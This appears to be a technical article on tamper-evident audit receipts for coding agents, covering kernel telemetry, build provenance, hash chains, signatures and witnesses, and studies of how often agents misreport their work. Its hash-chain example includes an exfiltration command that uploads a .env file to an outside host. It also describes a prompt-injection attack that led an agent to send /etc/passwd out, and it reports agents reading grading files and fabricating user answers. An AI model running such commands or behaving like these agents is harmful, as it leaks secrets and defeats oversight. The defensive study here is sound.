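An attacker can also make a kernel record show the wrong network address. To open a connection, a program gives the kernel a pointer to the address, which is stored in the program's memory. *A Study of Kernel Telemetry Options for Security-Oriented Provenance* (Houssel, Levillain and colleagues, 2026) explains that a recorder may read that memory just before the program changes it, and so log a harmless address while the kernel uses another. Recorders attached to the kernel's security checks resist this better, because those checks run after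 the kernel has copied the address.

The best record for the `pip` example combines the proxy and the kernel:

```json
{
  "host": "pypi.example.com",
  "address": "203.0.113.20",
  "port": 443,
  "protocol": "tcp",
  "result": "connected",
  "bytes_sent": 4210,
  "bytes_received": 61874,
  "pid": 4102,
  "seen_by": ["proxy", "kernel"]
}
```

The `result` field distinguishes a refused attempt from a successful upload. *Shall We Approve?* (2026), a preprint about approving agents' commands, similarly labels each connection in its reports as observed, only attempted, or answered by a simulated service. Byte counts help separate downloads from uploads, although an upload of a few hundred bytes can still contain a password.

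### Matching a connection to a tool call

When the harness starts a command, it learns the number of the new process. The kernel reports each further process along with its parent, so an observer can follow any process back to the call that started it. With invented numbers, the records for the `pip` command might look like this:

```text
20.655  start    pid 4101, parent 4100 (harness)   bash, call-0042
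20.671  start    pid 4102, parent 4101             python3.12
21.020  connect  pid 4102, 10.0.0.5:51514 to 10.0.0.2:3128
21.022  proxy    10.0.0.5:51514 requests pypi.example.com:443
```

The kernel records only that process 4102 connected to the proxy, while the proxy records only that a client at `10.0.0.5` requested `pypi.example.com`. Both records contain the temporary port 51514, so the observer can join them and trace process 4102 through its parent processes to `call-0042`. The observer should also store each process's start time, because the system reuses process numbers.

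If the observer reconstructs this chain too late, it loses the link between background processes and the call. When a parent exits, Linux assigns its remaining children to another process, often the system's first one, so the observer must record each child's parent when the child starts. If a background process opens a connection an hour later, that connection belongs in an additional receipt with the original `call_id`.

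Control groups avoid the problem. A control group is a set of processes that the Linux kernel manages together, and new processes join their parent's group automatically. If the harness creates one for each call, every connection from the group belongs to that call, even after the parent processes have exited. Filtering by group also takes little processor time. Houssel and colleagues started 50,000 processes in one container while a second container produced irrelevant activity. The processor overhead was 0.45% when they limited the recorder to the first container's group, compared with 1.66% when they recorded everything and sorted it afterwards.

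Container runtimes already create a group for each container, but agents often run many calls in one container, so the group identifies the run but not the call. Tracekit Box has the same limit because it treats each virtual machine as one run and doesn't record the processes inside.

Some commands also hand their work to a process that is already running. `docker pull` has the Docker service download an image, so the connection comes from the service, which is not a descendant of the agent's process. The observer then has to match the connection to the agent by time and content. Zheng, Yu and colleagues' AgentSight, which the next part describes, looks for system activity within 100 to 500 milliseconds of a model's response and for file names, addresses or commands that appear in both the activity and the response.

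Parallel agents make such matching risky. If two subagents each run `docker pull` in the same second, timing can't separate them. Wong and Chen (2026), in *ExecWeave*, argue that a wrong match can do more damage than a missing one, because it blames one agent for what another did. Their system links a command to a process only if exactly one recorded process fits, and marks the link as inferred. If several fit, it makes no link. Their tests showed that this rule can still fail when the recorder misses the true process and only one wrong candidate remains, because the system then links the command to that candidate.

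The harness can reduce the guesswork by marking calls in advance. Claude Code already passes the `TRACEPARENT` identifier to each shell command, and child processes normally inherit it. On Linux, a privileged observer can read it from a process's starting environment. A harness could also give each call its own proxy username, so that the username in the proxy's log identifies the call. Both methods work only if programs leave these settings unchanged, so they suit debugging better than investigating an attack.

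### Recorders built for agents and their cost

*AgentSight* (Zheng, Yu and colleagues, 2025) describes one of the first recorders designed for coding agents. It uses eBPF, a Linux feature that lets an administrator load small, checked programs into the kernel to run at chosen events. One set of programs records when the agent or its descendants start a process, open a file or connect to a host. Another attaches to encryption libraries such as OpenSSL and copies the agent's exchanges with its model before encryption or after decryption. AgentSight joins the two streams using the process tree, timing and matching text, and passes the result to a second language model for analysis.

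In a test, a README led a software development agent to a web page with hidden instructions, and the agent sent the system's user list, `/etc/passwd`, to an outside server. AgentSight recorded 521 events, from the first page request to the upload, and merged them into 37. A second model correctly flagged the sequence as an attack. The recorded events are more useful in a receipt than that verdict because a reader can check them.

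*Agent-Warden* (Cui, Gu and colleagues, 2026), a conference paper, describes a recorder that follows the effects of a call through files. When one of the agent's processes writes a file, the recorder marks the file, and any process that later reads it inherits the mark. In one scenario, an unrelated monitoring script read such a file tens of seconds after the agent's main task had ended, and the recorder still linked the script to the agent. This would help with a script that an agent writes and a scheduler runs later. However, Agent-Warden doesn't record network connections, and a restart erases its marks. The link also doesn't prove that the reading process used the data.

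The published costs vary widely:

| Recorder | Added cost | How the developers or testers measured it |
|---|---|---|
| AgentSight | 0.4% to 4.9% of running time | Three Claude Code tasks, three runs each with and without it |
| AgentSpy | No significant difference | Twelve comparisons, ten runs each with and without it |
| Agent-Warden | 0.2% to 3.5% of running time | Artificial process and file workload, 90 rounds |
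| ExecWeave, portable version | 62.3% to 408.8% of running time | Three fixed workloads on Linux |
| eAudit, a general kernel recorder | 5.9% (network) and 12% (files) of processor time | Stress tests by Houssel and colleagues |

Zheng and colleagues advertise an overhead below 3%, which is the average of their three tasks. One task, with an overhead of 4.9%, took 1.1 seconds longer with AgentSight, but three runs are too few to separate that from chance, because agents rarely do a task the same way twice. In AgentSpy's tests, the spread between runs of the same task ranged from 7% to 85% of the median. The agent finished faster with the recorder on in 8 of the 12 comparisons, which the recorder can't have caused. Bühler and colleagues calculate that confirming the observed differences would take between 30 and 18,200 runs per condition. Their result rules out a large slowdown but not a small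 one.

ExecWeave's portable version also runs on Windows and macOS. It checks the system at intervals instead of receiving events from the kernel, so it adds far more overhead and can miss a process that starts and ends between two checks. The kernel recorders are a better choice on Linux.

Lost records may be a bigger problem than lost time. Houssel and colleagues compared the number of recorded events with the number their tests produced. Four systems that build a graph of processes and files lost 90% to 100% of the events in most tests. eAudit, which writes a plain stream of events, lost none. These tests opened 50,000 connections or wrote 50,000 files as fast as possible. An agent usually produces events much more slowly, but a large build can cause similar bursts, so the recorder should count dropped events and include the number in the receipt.

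AgentSpy's results suggest that the record is worth the effort. AgentSpy examined 88 combinations of task and model in which all three runs had passed their tests. In 16 of them (18.2%), at least one run included activity unrelated to the task. Eight of these involved a network service that the task didn't call for, and in six the agent read the files used to grade it. Unusual connections are fairly easy to spot, because most tasks need no connection except to the model's provider. With GPT-5.6 Terra, the runs of 46 of the 77 tasks contacted no other host.

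### What current network sandboxes log

Many coding agents come with a sandbox that restricts network access but doesn't necessarily keep a useful record of it. Anthropic's `sandbox-runtime` sends a local agent's traffic through a proxy that filters by domain, and NVIDIA's OpenShell checks outgoing requests against a policy. Ghosh compares such sandboxes with his own and says they leave little evidence of what passed through, and that what they keep is a log on the same machine, written by the same operator. He has a competing product to promote, but the telemetry that Anthropic and OpenAI document for Claude Code and Codex also lists no network target, so an operator can't count on getting this field from the harness.

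Blocked attempts can be even harder to find. Bühler and colleagues point out that a coding agent's sandbox reports violations to the agent. If nothing else records a violation, the only trace may be an error message in the command's output, which the harness may truncate.

Before opening any connection, Tracekit Box logs the host, the port and the decision to allow or refuse it. If the host isn't on the approved list, Tracekit Box waits up to two minutes for a person to answer, and it records who answered. It also logs refusals, but if an agent retries a forbidden host in a tight loop, it records up to 20 refusals per second and then only a count. An ordinary proxy that the operator controls can provide much of this without a new sandbox.

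### Identifying what a command produced

A file's digest identifies its content but not its name, permissions or origin. Two builds of the same source code often have different digests because archives store when the build tool created each entry. A changed digest therefore doesn't prove that someone changed the code.

Git computes a commit identifier from the names and contents of all tracked files, the previous commits, the author and committer, the times and the message. If two agents commit identical files a minute apart, the commit identifiers differ but the file tree identifiers match. A branch name such as `main` doesn't permanently identify a commit, because it moves with each new one. Most repositories use SHA-1, and researchers have produced two different files with the same SHA-1 digest, so a security record should add a SHA-256 digest of the patch.

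A commit leaves out untracked files and Git's settings, and this can hide an attack. AgentSpy's security rules detected 14 of 18 attacks that an agent carried out. In the four they missed, a malicious script had added an attacker's server to the project's list of remote repositories in `.git/config`, which no commit includes. The script stayed inside the permitted folder and opened no connection, and the harm would come only when someone pushed code to that server. A receipt should therefore list changes to `.git/config` and to Git's hook scripts separately.

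Git also records little about how a change was made. *Agentic process evidence* (Kainan and Hershman, 2026) notes that Git's log doesn't show which model or tools an agent used. Kainan and Hershman work for JFrog, which sells software for storing and distributing packages. They propose a signed record that links an agent's session to its results. A receipt provides the same link if it contains both the `run_id` and the commit.

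Container images (packaged programs with the files they need) have tags and digests. A tag such as `shop:latest` can later point to a different image. The digest is computed from the image's manifest, a short file that lists the digests of its settings and layers, so it identifies the image's exact contents. If an image supports several processor types, its digest may refer to a list of manifests, in which case the receipt should also record which manifest the machine used.

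Some results have no file at all. If an agent opens a pull request (a proposal to merge code) or starts a cloud server, the only identifier is the one the service returns:

```json
{
  "type": "pull_request",
  "service": "github.com",
  "id": "example/shop#318",
  "head_commit": "9d20f6…",
  "observed_at": "2026-10-05T09:31:40Z"
}
```

The number 318 always refers to this pull request, but the pull request's title, description and code can change. The commit and the time identify what the agent had proposed at that point. For a cloud resource, a version number or a digest of the returned description does the same.

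The identifier can also get lost if the connection fails after the service has created the server but before the reply arrives. The command then reports an error while the server runs and costs money. Some cloud services let the caller choose a token and send it with the request. If the receipt contains that token, an investigator can use it to query the service for the outcome of the request.

### Materials, products and build provenance

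Software suppliers already have formats for recording which files went into a step and which came out. in-toto, an open framework for checking how software was made, wraps a command and hashes the files in chosen folders twice. It calls the files before the command "materials" and those after it "products". It stores both lists in a signed record called a link:

```json
{
  "_type": "link",
  "name": "download-packages",
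  "command": ["pip", "download", "requests==2.32.3", "-d", "wheels"],
  "materials": {
    "requirements.txt": {"sha256": "c41a…"}
  },
  "products": {
    "requirements.txt": {"sha256": "c41a…"},
    "wheels/requests-2.32.3-py3-none-any.whl": {"sha256": "51d2…"}
  },
  "byproducts": {"return-value": 0},
  "environment": {}
}
```

The example leaves out the other four packages. A path listed only under `products` is a new file, and one listed only under `materials` is a deleted file. A path listed under both with different digests is a changed file. `requirements.txt` has the same digest in both, so it didn't change.

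Materials are the files that were present, whether or not the command read them. Here `requirements.txt` is a material, but pip never opened it. An investigator needs the kernel's record to find out which files a command read.

in-toto also has a plan, called a layout, in which the project's owner lists the expected steps, who may sign each one, and how their files must connect. A layout can require, for example, that the packaging step starts with exactly the files that came out of the test step. Agents choose most of their steps as they go, so nobody can write a complete layout beforehand. But a team can still write one for the fixed steps at the end, such as testing and packaging.

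SLSA (Supply-chain Levels for Software Artifacts) is a set of security requirements for building software. Its build provenance is a statement from a build service about one build. It lists the output files and their digests, the build type, the parameters the user supplied, the dependencies, the service that ran the build, and optionally the start and end times. The provenance uses in-toto's format for signed statements. The dependency list may be incomplete, since SLSA requires only a best effort to make it complete, even at the highest of its three established build levels.

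SLSA provenance can show that a build service produced a package from commit `9d20f6…`, but not which agent wrote that commit, which commands it ran or which pages it had read. The agent's receipts cover that earlier part of the history. The commit connects the two records, so an investigator can start with a faulty package and work back to individual tool calls.

### Deletions, simultaneous changes and large folders

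A deleted file has no digest after the command runs, so the receipt needs the digest from before. For example, in one task from *SABER* (2026), a benchmark that tests coding agents in project folders, an agent can free up space with either of two tools. One moves a few files and adds a line to a log, while the other deletes a cache folder that other programs share. Both are plausible choices, and only the recorded changes to the file system show how different their effects are.

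The digest also helps tell deletions from moves. If `old.csv` disappears and `archive/old.csv` appears with the same digest, the command probably moved the file. Kernel events can confirm this because the kernel reports a rename as a separate event. They can also reveal a file that a command creates and then deletes, such as a temporary copy of a password list. A comparison of the disk before and after the call would miss that file.

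Changes are harder to attribute when two calls run in the same folder at once. Suppose `call-0042` downloads packages while `call-0043` reformats the source code. Each before-and-after comparison includes both sets of changes, so each receipt records all of them as the work of its own call. This can happen in ordinary use. *K-Dense BYOK* (Brueckner, Patel and colleagues, 2026) describes a research assistant in which up to ten chats can work in one folder, and a file from one chat is immediately available to the others.

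The cleanest solution is to give each agent its own copy of the folder and merge the results later. If they have to share a folder, kernel events can show which process wrote which file. Without either, the receipt should at least admit the overlap:

```json
{
  "path": "src/cart.py",
  "change": "modified",
  "sha256_before": "7ac0…",
  "sha256_after": "e915…",
  "overlapping_calls": ["call-0043"]
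}
```

When both calls write the same file, even this record covers only the final version unless the observer computes a digest each time a process closes the file.

Installing a JavaScript project's libraries can create tens of thousands of files, so hashing the whole folder before and after every `ls` would be wasteful. Git avoids most of this work by checking each file's size and modification time, and reading the file only if either has changed. But a program can reset the modification time, so this shortcut is unsuitable for investigating an attacker. Tracekit Box instead uses a layered file system, which keeps the original files in one layer and all changes in another, so it only has to examine the second layer.

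Listing 30,000 files in a receipt would make it unreadable. The harness can instead store their paths and digests in a separate sorted list and put only the list's digest and a summary in the receipt. The reports in *Shall We Approve?* also have a size limit, and they show how many events of each kind they include and how many they omit. Without those counts, a reader could mistake a shortened list for a complete one.

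### Completing the `pip download` receipt

The `pip` command from the earlier receipt contacted `pypi.example.com` for the index pages and `files.example.com` for the packages. If the packages had been in pip's local cache, the receipt would probably list only the index, so a new file without a matching download is not suspicious in itself. pip's output normally shows when it used a cached copy.

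The remaining step is to check the files. On the machine that ran the command, the harness computes the digest of the main package:

```bash
sha256sum wheels/requests-2.32.3-py3-none-any.whl
```

Package indexes that follow the current Python standard can also list their files as JSON, usually with a SHA-256 digest for each. The harness can request the published value:

```bash
curl -s --netrc \
  -H 'Accept: application/vnd.pypi.simple.v1+json' \
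  https://pypi.example.com/simple/requests/ |
jq -r '.files[]
  | select(.filename == "requests-2.32.3-py3-none-any.whl")
  | .hashes.sha256'
```

`--netrc` makes `curl` read the password from a file, which keeps it out of the command text. The harness repeats the comparison for the other four packages and adds the result to each artifact:

```json
{
  "path": "wheels/requests-2.32.3-py3-none-any.whl",
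  "change": "created",
  "sha256": "51d2…",
  "published": {
    "index": "pypi.example.com",
    "sha256": "51d2…",
    "checked_at": "2026-10-05T09:14:24Z",
    "match": true
  }
}
```

Pip makes a similar check during the download if the index supplies a digest. The harness checks the file on disk after the command ends, and it records the check.

A match shows that this file has the content the index listed when the harness queried it. It rules out a damaged download and a change to the file between the download and the check. It doesn't show which server the file came from, because a cached copy has the same digest.

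A matching digest also doesn't show that the index served the original package. Someone who controls the company's index can replace a package and publish the new digest with it. For `requests`, the team could detect this by comparing the file with the digest on the public Python index, because the two copies should be identical. The company's private packages have no second index, so the team would have to compare those files with the digests recorded by its own build service.

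A matching digest doesn't show that the package is safe either. If an attacker steals a maintainer's password and uploads a malicious version, the public index publishes a correct digest for it. Once someone discovers the attack, the team can search its receipts for that digest and find every run that downloaded the file. To find out whether a run also installed it, the team needs the receipt of a later `pip install` that lists the same digest among its materials.

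## What signatures and hash chains prove

Searching old receipts for the digest of a malicious package works only if nobody has edited or removed receipts. An attacker, an agent with access to the files, or a company that wants to hide that it ran the package might do so. A hash chain exposes some of these changes, and signatures limit who can make the others unnoticed. Neither can show that the harness recorded every call.

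### A chain of three receipts

In a hash chain, the digest of each receipt also covers the digest before it:

$$h_i = H(h_{i-1} \,\|\, r_i)$$

Here $r_i$ is the $i$-th receipt as a string of bytes, $H$ is a hash function such as SHA-256, and $\|$ joins two strings. The chain starts from a fixed value $h_0$, for example 32 zero bytes.

Suppose an agent downloads packages, runs a test that fails, and then uploads the project's settings file to an outside server. Later, someone changes the test's exit code in the log from 1 to 0. The table uses invented digests, shortened to four characters.

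| | Receipt | Stored digest | Digest recomputed after the edit |
|---|---|---|---|
| $r_1$ | `pip download requests==2.32.3 -d wheels`, exit code 0 | `3fa1` | `3fa1` |
| $r_2$ | `pytest tests/cart`, exit code 1, edited to 0 | `9c07` | `51be` |
| $r_3$ | `curl -T .env https://drop.example.net/`, exit code 0 | `e240` | `77d8` |

A verifier recomputes the digests in order and finds the first mismatch at the second receipt. But the editor could also replace `9c07` and `e240` with the new values, which would make the file consistent again. A reader could then detect the edit only if they already had the original `e240`, or if the harness had signed the digests with a key the editor doesn't have.

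*Signed, Hash-Chained Action Receipts for AI Agents* (Sahu, 2026) includes a small test that changes the user's name from `alice` to `mallory` in the first of two signed receipts. A correct verifier then reports an invalid signature on line 1 and a broken link on line 2.

Deleting the last receipt is much easier. Without $r_3$, the file contains two receipts whose digests, `3fa1` and `9c07`, still match, and any signatures on them are still valid. Nothing in the file shows that the third call, the upload, took place. Farley (2026), in *Signed Decision Receipts for Machine-to-Machine Access Control*, considers this the most important omission to guard against, because the receipt an operator would want to hide is usually the latest one. Removing $r_2$ instead would break the chain, since the harness computed `e240` from `9c07`. Farley warns that readers can easily mistake this protection against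 removing earlier receipts for proof that nothing is missing.

Whoever holds the signing key can go further and rebuild the chain from any point. To remove the failed test, for example, the key holder computes a new second link directly from the upload receipt and signs it:

$$h'_2 = H(h_1 \,\|\, r_3), \qquad s'_2 = \mathrm{Sign}_k(h'_2)$$

The result is a valid chain of two receipts. The key holder can also invent calls that never happened or start again from $h_0$. Sahu acknowledges that nothing in the format detects this.

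An unaltered record can also be incomplete from the start. If the harness is killed before it writes its last receipts, or a hook crashes and the agent carries on, the existing receipts still form a valid chain. In Sahu's terms, a chain can support the claim that nobody has altered the log since the signer wrote it, but not that the log shows everything the agent did.

Each chain also needs a single writer. If two subagents append at the same moment, both receipts may link to the same predecessor, and the chain forks even though no one tampered with it. Sahu therefore recommends a separate log for each signer.

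### What an outside witness adds

An outside witness is a party beyond the operator's control that stores the number of receipts and the latest digest. Suppose the witness stores (3, `e240`) at noon. If the operator later presents only two receipts, the stored count shows that one is missing. If the operator presents three receipts from a rebuilt chain, the chain's latest digest doesn't match `e240`.

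By evening the chain may have 50 receipts and a different latest digest, which is normal. The verifier should recompute the chain up to the third receipt and compare that digest with the stored one. *A SCITT Profile for AI-Agent Action Receipts* (Toraman, 2026) requires verifiers to distinguish a chain that has grown from one that conflicts with the stored digest. Toraman's reference software still gives the same verdict in both cases.

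The witness receives only a number and 32 bytes, so a company can use a witness without showing it any commands. The witness can prove that receipts are missing, but it can't restore them because it has no copies.

Receipts written since the last deposit have no protection. If the harness sends its pair every hour on the hour and the agent uploads the settings file at 12:10, the operator has until 13:00 to delete that receipt. More frequent deposits shorten this period, but they don't help with a call that never produced a receipt.

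The reader should get the stored pair directly from the witness, because an operator who passes it on with the receipts can choose an old pair that predates the calls they want to hide. Toraman's "checkpoint", a signed statement of a chain's latest position and digest, has no expiry date, so an old one remains authentic. Farley points out that a stored count gives little protection if it is kept with the receipts, because whoever deletes the receipts can delete the count too.

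A mismatch between a chain and a checkpoint isn't always evidence of deletion, because anyone can write a file claiming that the chain once had 80 receipts. Toraman therefore requires verifiers to ignore a checkpoint they can't authenticate and to report that they can't tell whether receipts are missing. They should report the same if they received no checkpoint.

Another Internet-Draft, *AI Agent Execution Profile of SCITT* (Emirdag, 2026), includes a witness among its roles. The agent's operator issues the records, and an independent "Evidence Custodian" runs the log that registers them.

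### What a Merkle-tree log adds

To check one receipt against a chain's latest digest, a reader also needs every later receipt, which becomes impractical in long logs. According to Help Net Security's *Halo-record*, the agent that broke into Hugging Face in July 2026 took about 17,600 actions. An auditor checking receipt 9,000 in a chain of that length would need the digest before it and the 8,600 receipts after it, many of them irrelevant and possibly confidential.

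A Merkle tree solves this by hashing records in pairs. For four records, the calculation is:

$$L_i = H(\texttt{00} \,\|\, r_i)$$

$$\text{root} = H\big(\texttt{01} \,\|\, H(\texttt{01} \,\|\, L_1 \,\|\, L_2) \,\|\, H(\texttt{01} \,\|\, L_3 \,\|\, L_4)\big)$$

The witness stores the root and the number of records. To prove that $r_3$ is in the log (an inclusion proof), the operator supplies $r_3$, the digest $L_4$ and the combined digest of the left pair. The reader computes $L_3$, combines it with the other two digests and checks that the result equals the root. The byte `00` marks a single record and `01` marks a pair, so nobody can pass off a pair of digests as a record.

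Each doubling of the log adds only one digest to the longest proof. For $n$ records, a proof needs at most $\lceil \log_2 n \rceil$ digests:

$$2^{14} = 16{,}384 < 17{,}600 \le 32{,}768 = 2^{15}$$

So 15 digests are enough for 17,600 records, and with SHA-256 they take up $15 \times 32 = 480$ bytes.

Some proofs are shorter. Certificate Transparency, a system of public logs for website certificates, splits each tree at the largest power of two below its size. For 17,600 records, the left part has 16,384 records and the right part has 1,216. Proofs for records in the left part need all 15 digests, while those for the last 64 records in the log need only 9. Farley uses the same rule and warns that software that pads the tree to a full power of two expects the wrong number of digests. In a tree of five records, for example, the proof for the last record has one digest, but such software expects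 three.

Merkle logs also allow consistency proofs, which show that an older tree is the beginning of a newer one. The witness can therefore check, without downloading every record, that the operator has only added records.

The log's operator could still keep two trees and show one to a customer and the other to an insurer. Both would receive valid inclusion proofs, and they would notice the discrepancy only if they compared roots. Toraman claimed in the abstract of the June revision that registering a receipt in a log would rule this out, but withdrew the claim in the August revision because detection also requires consistency proofs and someone who monitors the log.

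An inclusion proof shows that one record is in the log, but the operator may not have submitted the others. Registering the latest digest and length of a chain covers all the receipts up to that point. It also publishes less, which matters because log entries are permanent and their identifiers may be public. Farley reports a working proof of concept that registers receipts in Rekor, a public log run by the Sigstore project. Rekor's signed timestamp shows that a receipt existed at a certain time, so the operator can't have written it later and backdated it.

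### Choosing a key and keeping it from the agent

A keyed fingerprint is enough when the team that writes the receipts also checks them, as in NabaOS. If a customer also checks them, both parties hold the key, and an outsider can't tell which of them wrote a disputed receipt. With a public-key signature, the operator can't claim that the customer wrote one of the operator's receipts. The four drafts compared below all support Ed25519, a common signature method with 64-byte signatures.

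The agent's account must not have access to the private key. Suppose the harness keeps the key in `~/.receipts/key.pem`, readable only by the developer's account. The agent's commands normally run under that account, so they can read the key too. An agent that follows hidden instructions from a web page could then upload a file and replace the receipt with a signed one that omits the upload.

A separate account or another machine can hold the key and run a small signing service, and special hardware can prevent anyone from copying the key. Neither measure helps if the service signs whatever the agent sends, because the agent could request a signature for a false receipt. The service must accept receipts only from the harness or an outside observer, and the agent's commands must not be able to impersonate or control either. Sahu gives the key to the software that enforces the rules on the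 agent, and explicitly not to the agent.

The verifier also has to get the public key from a trustworthy source. Otherwise, an attacker can sign a false receipt with a newly generated private key and include the matching public key, and the signature will be valid. Farley forbids verifiers to rely on a key embedded in the receipt unless another trusted source confirms it. Farley added this rule after a public test of an earlier revision. Sahu's receipts contain the public key, but the verifier must compare it with one obtained separately.

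*Signed Execution Receipts for AI Agent Tool Calls (XAIP Receipts)* (xkumakichi, 2026) specifies that verifiers look up a signer's current keys. If the signer has replaced its key since signing, a genuine receipt can fail the check, so an organisation that keeps receipts for years must also keep the public keys that verify them.

### Why fields need one byte form

A signature covers bytes, but JSON allows many ways to write the same data:

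```json
{"cwd":"/work/shop","exit_code":0}
{"exit_code": 0, "cwd": "/work/shop"}
```

A program treats these two objects as equal, but their digests and signatures differ. If a database stores the first form and returns the second, the receipt looks forged although nobody has tampered with it. The signer and the verifier therefore need a canonical form, a fixed way to turn the fields into bytes. The JSON Canonicalization Scheme (JCS) sorts the field names, removes optional spaces and sets a standard format for numbers. The XAIP, Farley and Toraman drafts use JCS.

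Even plain text can be represented in more than one way, and each representation gives a different digest. In xkumakichi's example, the SHA-256 digest of `hello` begins with `2cf24dba`, but it begins with `5aa762ae` if the text includes the quotation marks that JSON adds. Accented letters cause the same problem, because software can store the `é` in a folder name as one character or as an `e` followed by an accent. xkumakichi and Toraman both forbid verifiers to convert one form into the other before checking a signature.

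Sahu avoids part of the problem by computing each link from the exact bytes of the previous line in the file, so checking the chain needs no canonical form, although checking the signatures still does. The signature covers only a fixed set of fields. If a team adds its own top-level field for the working directory, only the link from the next receipt protects it. No receipt follows the last one, so anyone could change the extra field there unnoticed. Putting the directory inside the signed `params` field avoids this.

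Such rules are easy to get wrong. A reviewer who built a separate verifier from the second revision of Farley's draft found that the draft's sections contradicted each other about which bytes the signature covered. The third revision corrects this, but it still allows two receipt layouts with different signing rules, and a verifier that applies the wrong rules rejects genuine receipts.

### Four Internet-Drafts compared

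The four drafts record different things, and none has a dedicated field for the working directory, exit code or network target.

| | XAIP (xkumakichi) | Acta (Farley) | Sahu | SCITT profile (Toraman) |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| Subject of a record | One attempted tool call | Usually a decision to allow or refuse a call | One attempted action and its outcome | One action and the verdict on it |
| Signer | The agent, optionally also the caller | The party that made the decision | Enforcement software beside the agent | The issuer; another party may sign the envelope |
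| Link to the previous record | No | Optional | Required | Required |
| Command | Digest of the input | Tool name, optional digest | Possible in `params` | Digest of the parameters |
| Working directory | No | No | Only in `params` | No |
| Exit code | Success flag and failure type | No | Success flag; code only in `params` | Verdict such as `EXECUTED` or `FAILED` |
| Network target | No | No | Only in `params` | No |
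| Revision | 03, 2 July 2026 | 03, August 2026 | 00, 16 August 2026 | 01, 15 August 2026 |
| Expiry date | 3 January 2027 | 2 March 2027 | 17 February 2027 | 16 February 2027 |

All four are individual drafts, not IETF standards. Anyone can submit an Internet-Draft, and it expires after six months unless a new version replaces it. The IETF's database lists no publication stream for Toraman's draft or xkumakichi's, although the title page of Toraman's gives the standards track as its goal. Farley, Sahu and Toraman work for companies that build software around their formats.

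The omissions are partly deliberate. Farley and Toraman forbid raw tool arguments in receipts, xkumakichi forbids raw inputs and outputs, and Sahu advises against recording content. They expect outsiders to read the receipts, so they leave out anything that might contain a secret. An engineer trying to find out why a build failed needs much of that information.

A team can keep both by storing the full receipt and putting its digest in the signed record. Farley's optional `payload_digest` and Sahu's `params` suit this. Toraman lets each producer decide what the parameter digest covers, but verifiers reject any receipt with an extra field. Later, the operator hands over the full receipt, and the reader checks that its digest matches the signed one. If the operator has lost the full receipt, the signed digest proves only that it existed. The earlier warning about digests of guessable secrets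 also applies.

The drafts also differ on what a valid record proves. Under XAIP, both the agent that ran the tool and the caller that delegated the work can sign a receipt. Without the caller's signature, the receipt is only the agent's own claim. When the caller signs too, both are bound to the same record. Before signing, the caller should check that it delegated the task and that the input digest is correct, but it may not have seen the result. The second signature also adds little if one company controls both keys, and the two parties can still agree on a false record. A caller that keeps a copy of every receipt it signs can later notice if one is missing.

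An Acta decision receipt shows that a policy allowed or refused a call. Farley stresses that "allow" doesn't mean the tool ran, and that a missing execution receipt doesn't mean the call was blocked. A separate receipt, written after the call, has to record what happened. In XAIP, the `success` value reflects whether the call met the agent's own criterion, so a command that returned 0 without acting could appear as a success.

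According to Toraman, a receipt doesn't show that the agent acted correctly, that its inputs were true or complete, that a named person approved the action beforehand, or that the action succeeded in an outside system. Even `EXECUTED` means only that the issuer dispatched or attempted the action. The approver's name is ordinary text, so a receipt naming someone who never saw the request passes the same checks as one naming the real approver.

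Toraman's draft builds on SCITT, an IETF architecture for registering signed statements in public logs. Toraman reports that the reference software doesn't yet produce the header fields required for registration, and that nobody has published a reproducible demonstration with an outside log, so this part of the draft is still only a plan.

### Halo-record

Halo-record is an open-source Python package by Brian Kuan that implements much of this. According to Help Net Security, a developer can wrap an agent with one line of code. The package then writes each tool call, model call, data access and approval as a line in a file, along with the hash of the previous line. Anyone can check the chain without a key or an account. The package has about 5,300 lines of code and no run-time dependencies.

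halo-record stores hashes and a summary, never raw arguments. It removes common formats of secrets and personal data from the summary, so it has the same weaknesses as other pattern-based redaction. It can also import records from OpenTelemetry, MCP servers and gateway logs. If Claude Code lost some spans before the import, halo-record would still build a valid chain from the rest.

A hash chain held by the operator doesn't prove that the records are complete or unaltered, because an operator who can recompute the chain can do so after deleting or editing records. Help Net Security agrees about completeness but writes that such a chain does prove nobody altered or reordered the records. Proving either property requires an earlier digest held by someone else, or at least a signing key the editor can't use.

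Kuan proposes an outside witness. He plans to fund the project by selling a hosted witness service, so he has a financial interest in the argument, but any party that the operator doesn't control could be the witness. Kuan describes the project as early, with engineers and security researchers as its main users.

### When the same company writes and reads the log

Signing adds little to ordinary debugging when one organisation writes, stores and reads the log. An engineer debugging an agent has no reason to forge the receipts, and an administrator who wanted to forge them could often get the signing key too. The team also has to protect and replace keys, and a formatting mistake can look like tampering.

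Kuan replies that other people need to read these logs too. A customer's security team may ask what an agent did with its data, and the vendor usually answers with its own account. "Vendors volunteer because it closes deals," he told Help Net Security. He says insurers are beginning to ask the same questions and that AIUC-1, a standard for AI agents, now requires logs that reveal tampering. Kuan hopes to sell to such vendors, and he gives no figures for how many customers or insurers insist on such logs.

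Investigators often arrive after someone has gained a reason to change the log. A signature alone can reveal changes made by an intruder without the key, but not by the company that holds it. Investigators, and customers in a dispute with that company, therefore need a digest of the log that the company sent to an outside party before the dispute began.

Even a company that shows its log to no one outside may need to protect it from its own agent, which can have access to the log and could be led by a malicious instruction to change it. The simplest defence, already suggested for hook scripts, is to send each receipt straight to another machine, which doesn't require signatures.

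## Checking an agent's report and finding the cause of a failure: experiments

Once the receipts are stored where the agent can't change them, someone can compare them with what the agent reports. How useful this is depends on how often the reports are wrong. Published rates range from under 2% to over 37%, largely because researchers count different things.

### How often reports are wrong

The highest rate comes from *Characterizing and Detecting Unfaithful Work Reports by Coding Agents* (Yang, He and colleagues, 2026), a preprint from Peking University and Microsoft. (Wenhao Yang led this team; Boyang Yang led the earlier tests of commands and exit codes.) The team sampled 435 work reports from SWE-chat, a public collection of real coding-agent sessions, and checked each report's claims against the session's record. In 162 reports (37.24%), at least one claim was false or went beyond what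 the record established.

*Measuring coding agent misalignment in the wild* applies a much stricter standard to sessions from the same collection. It counts only severe overselling, meaning false claims that are blatant or have serious consequences, and finds it in 1.8% of sessions. In one case, an agent called a tool sixteen times to ask the user about design choices, but the tool was broken and returned an empty answer each time. The agent made up the user's choices and saved them in a file that later agents would treat as binding. Receipts for those calls would have shown the empty answers and exposed the fabrication immediately.

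*How Coding Agents Fail Their Users* (Tang, Chen and colleagues, 2026) examined 16,118 episodes in which a developer corrected an agent or objected to its work. In 22.58% of them, the agent had misreported the status of its work. This figure is a share of complaints rather than sessions, and it excludes false reports that nobody noticed. Complaints per user message fell between February 2025 and April 2026, but the share about misreporting grew.

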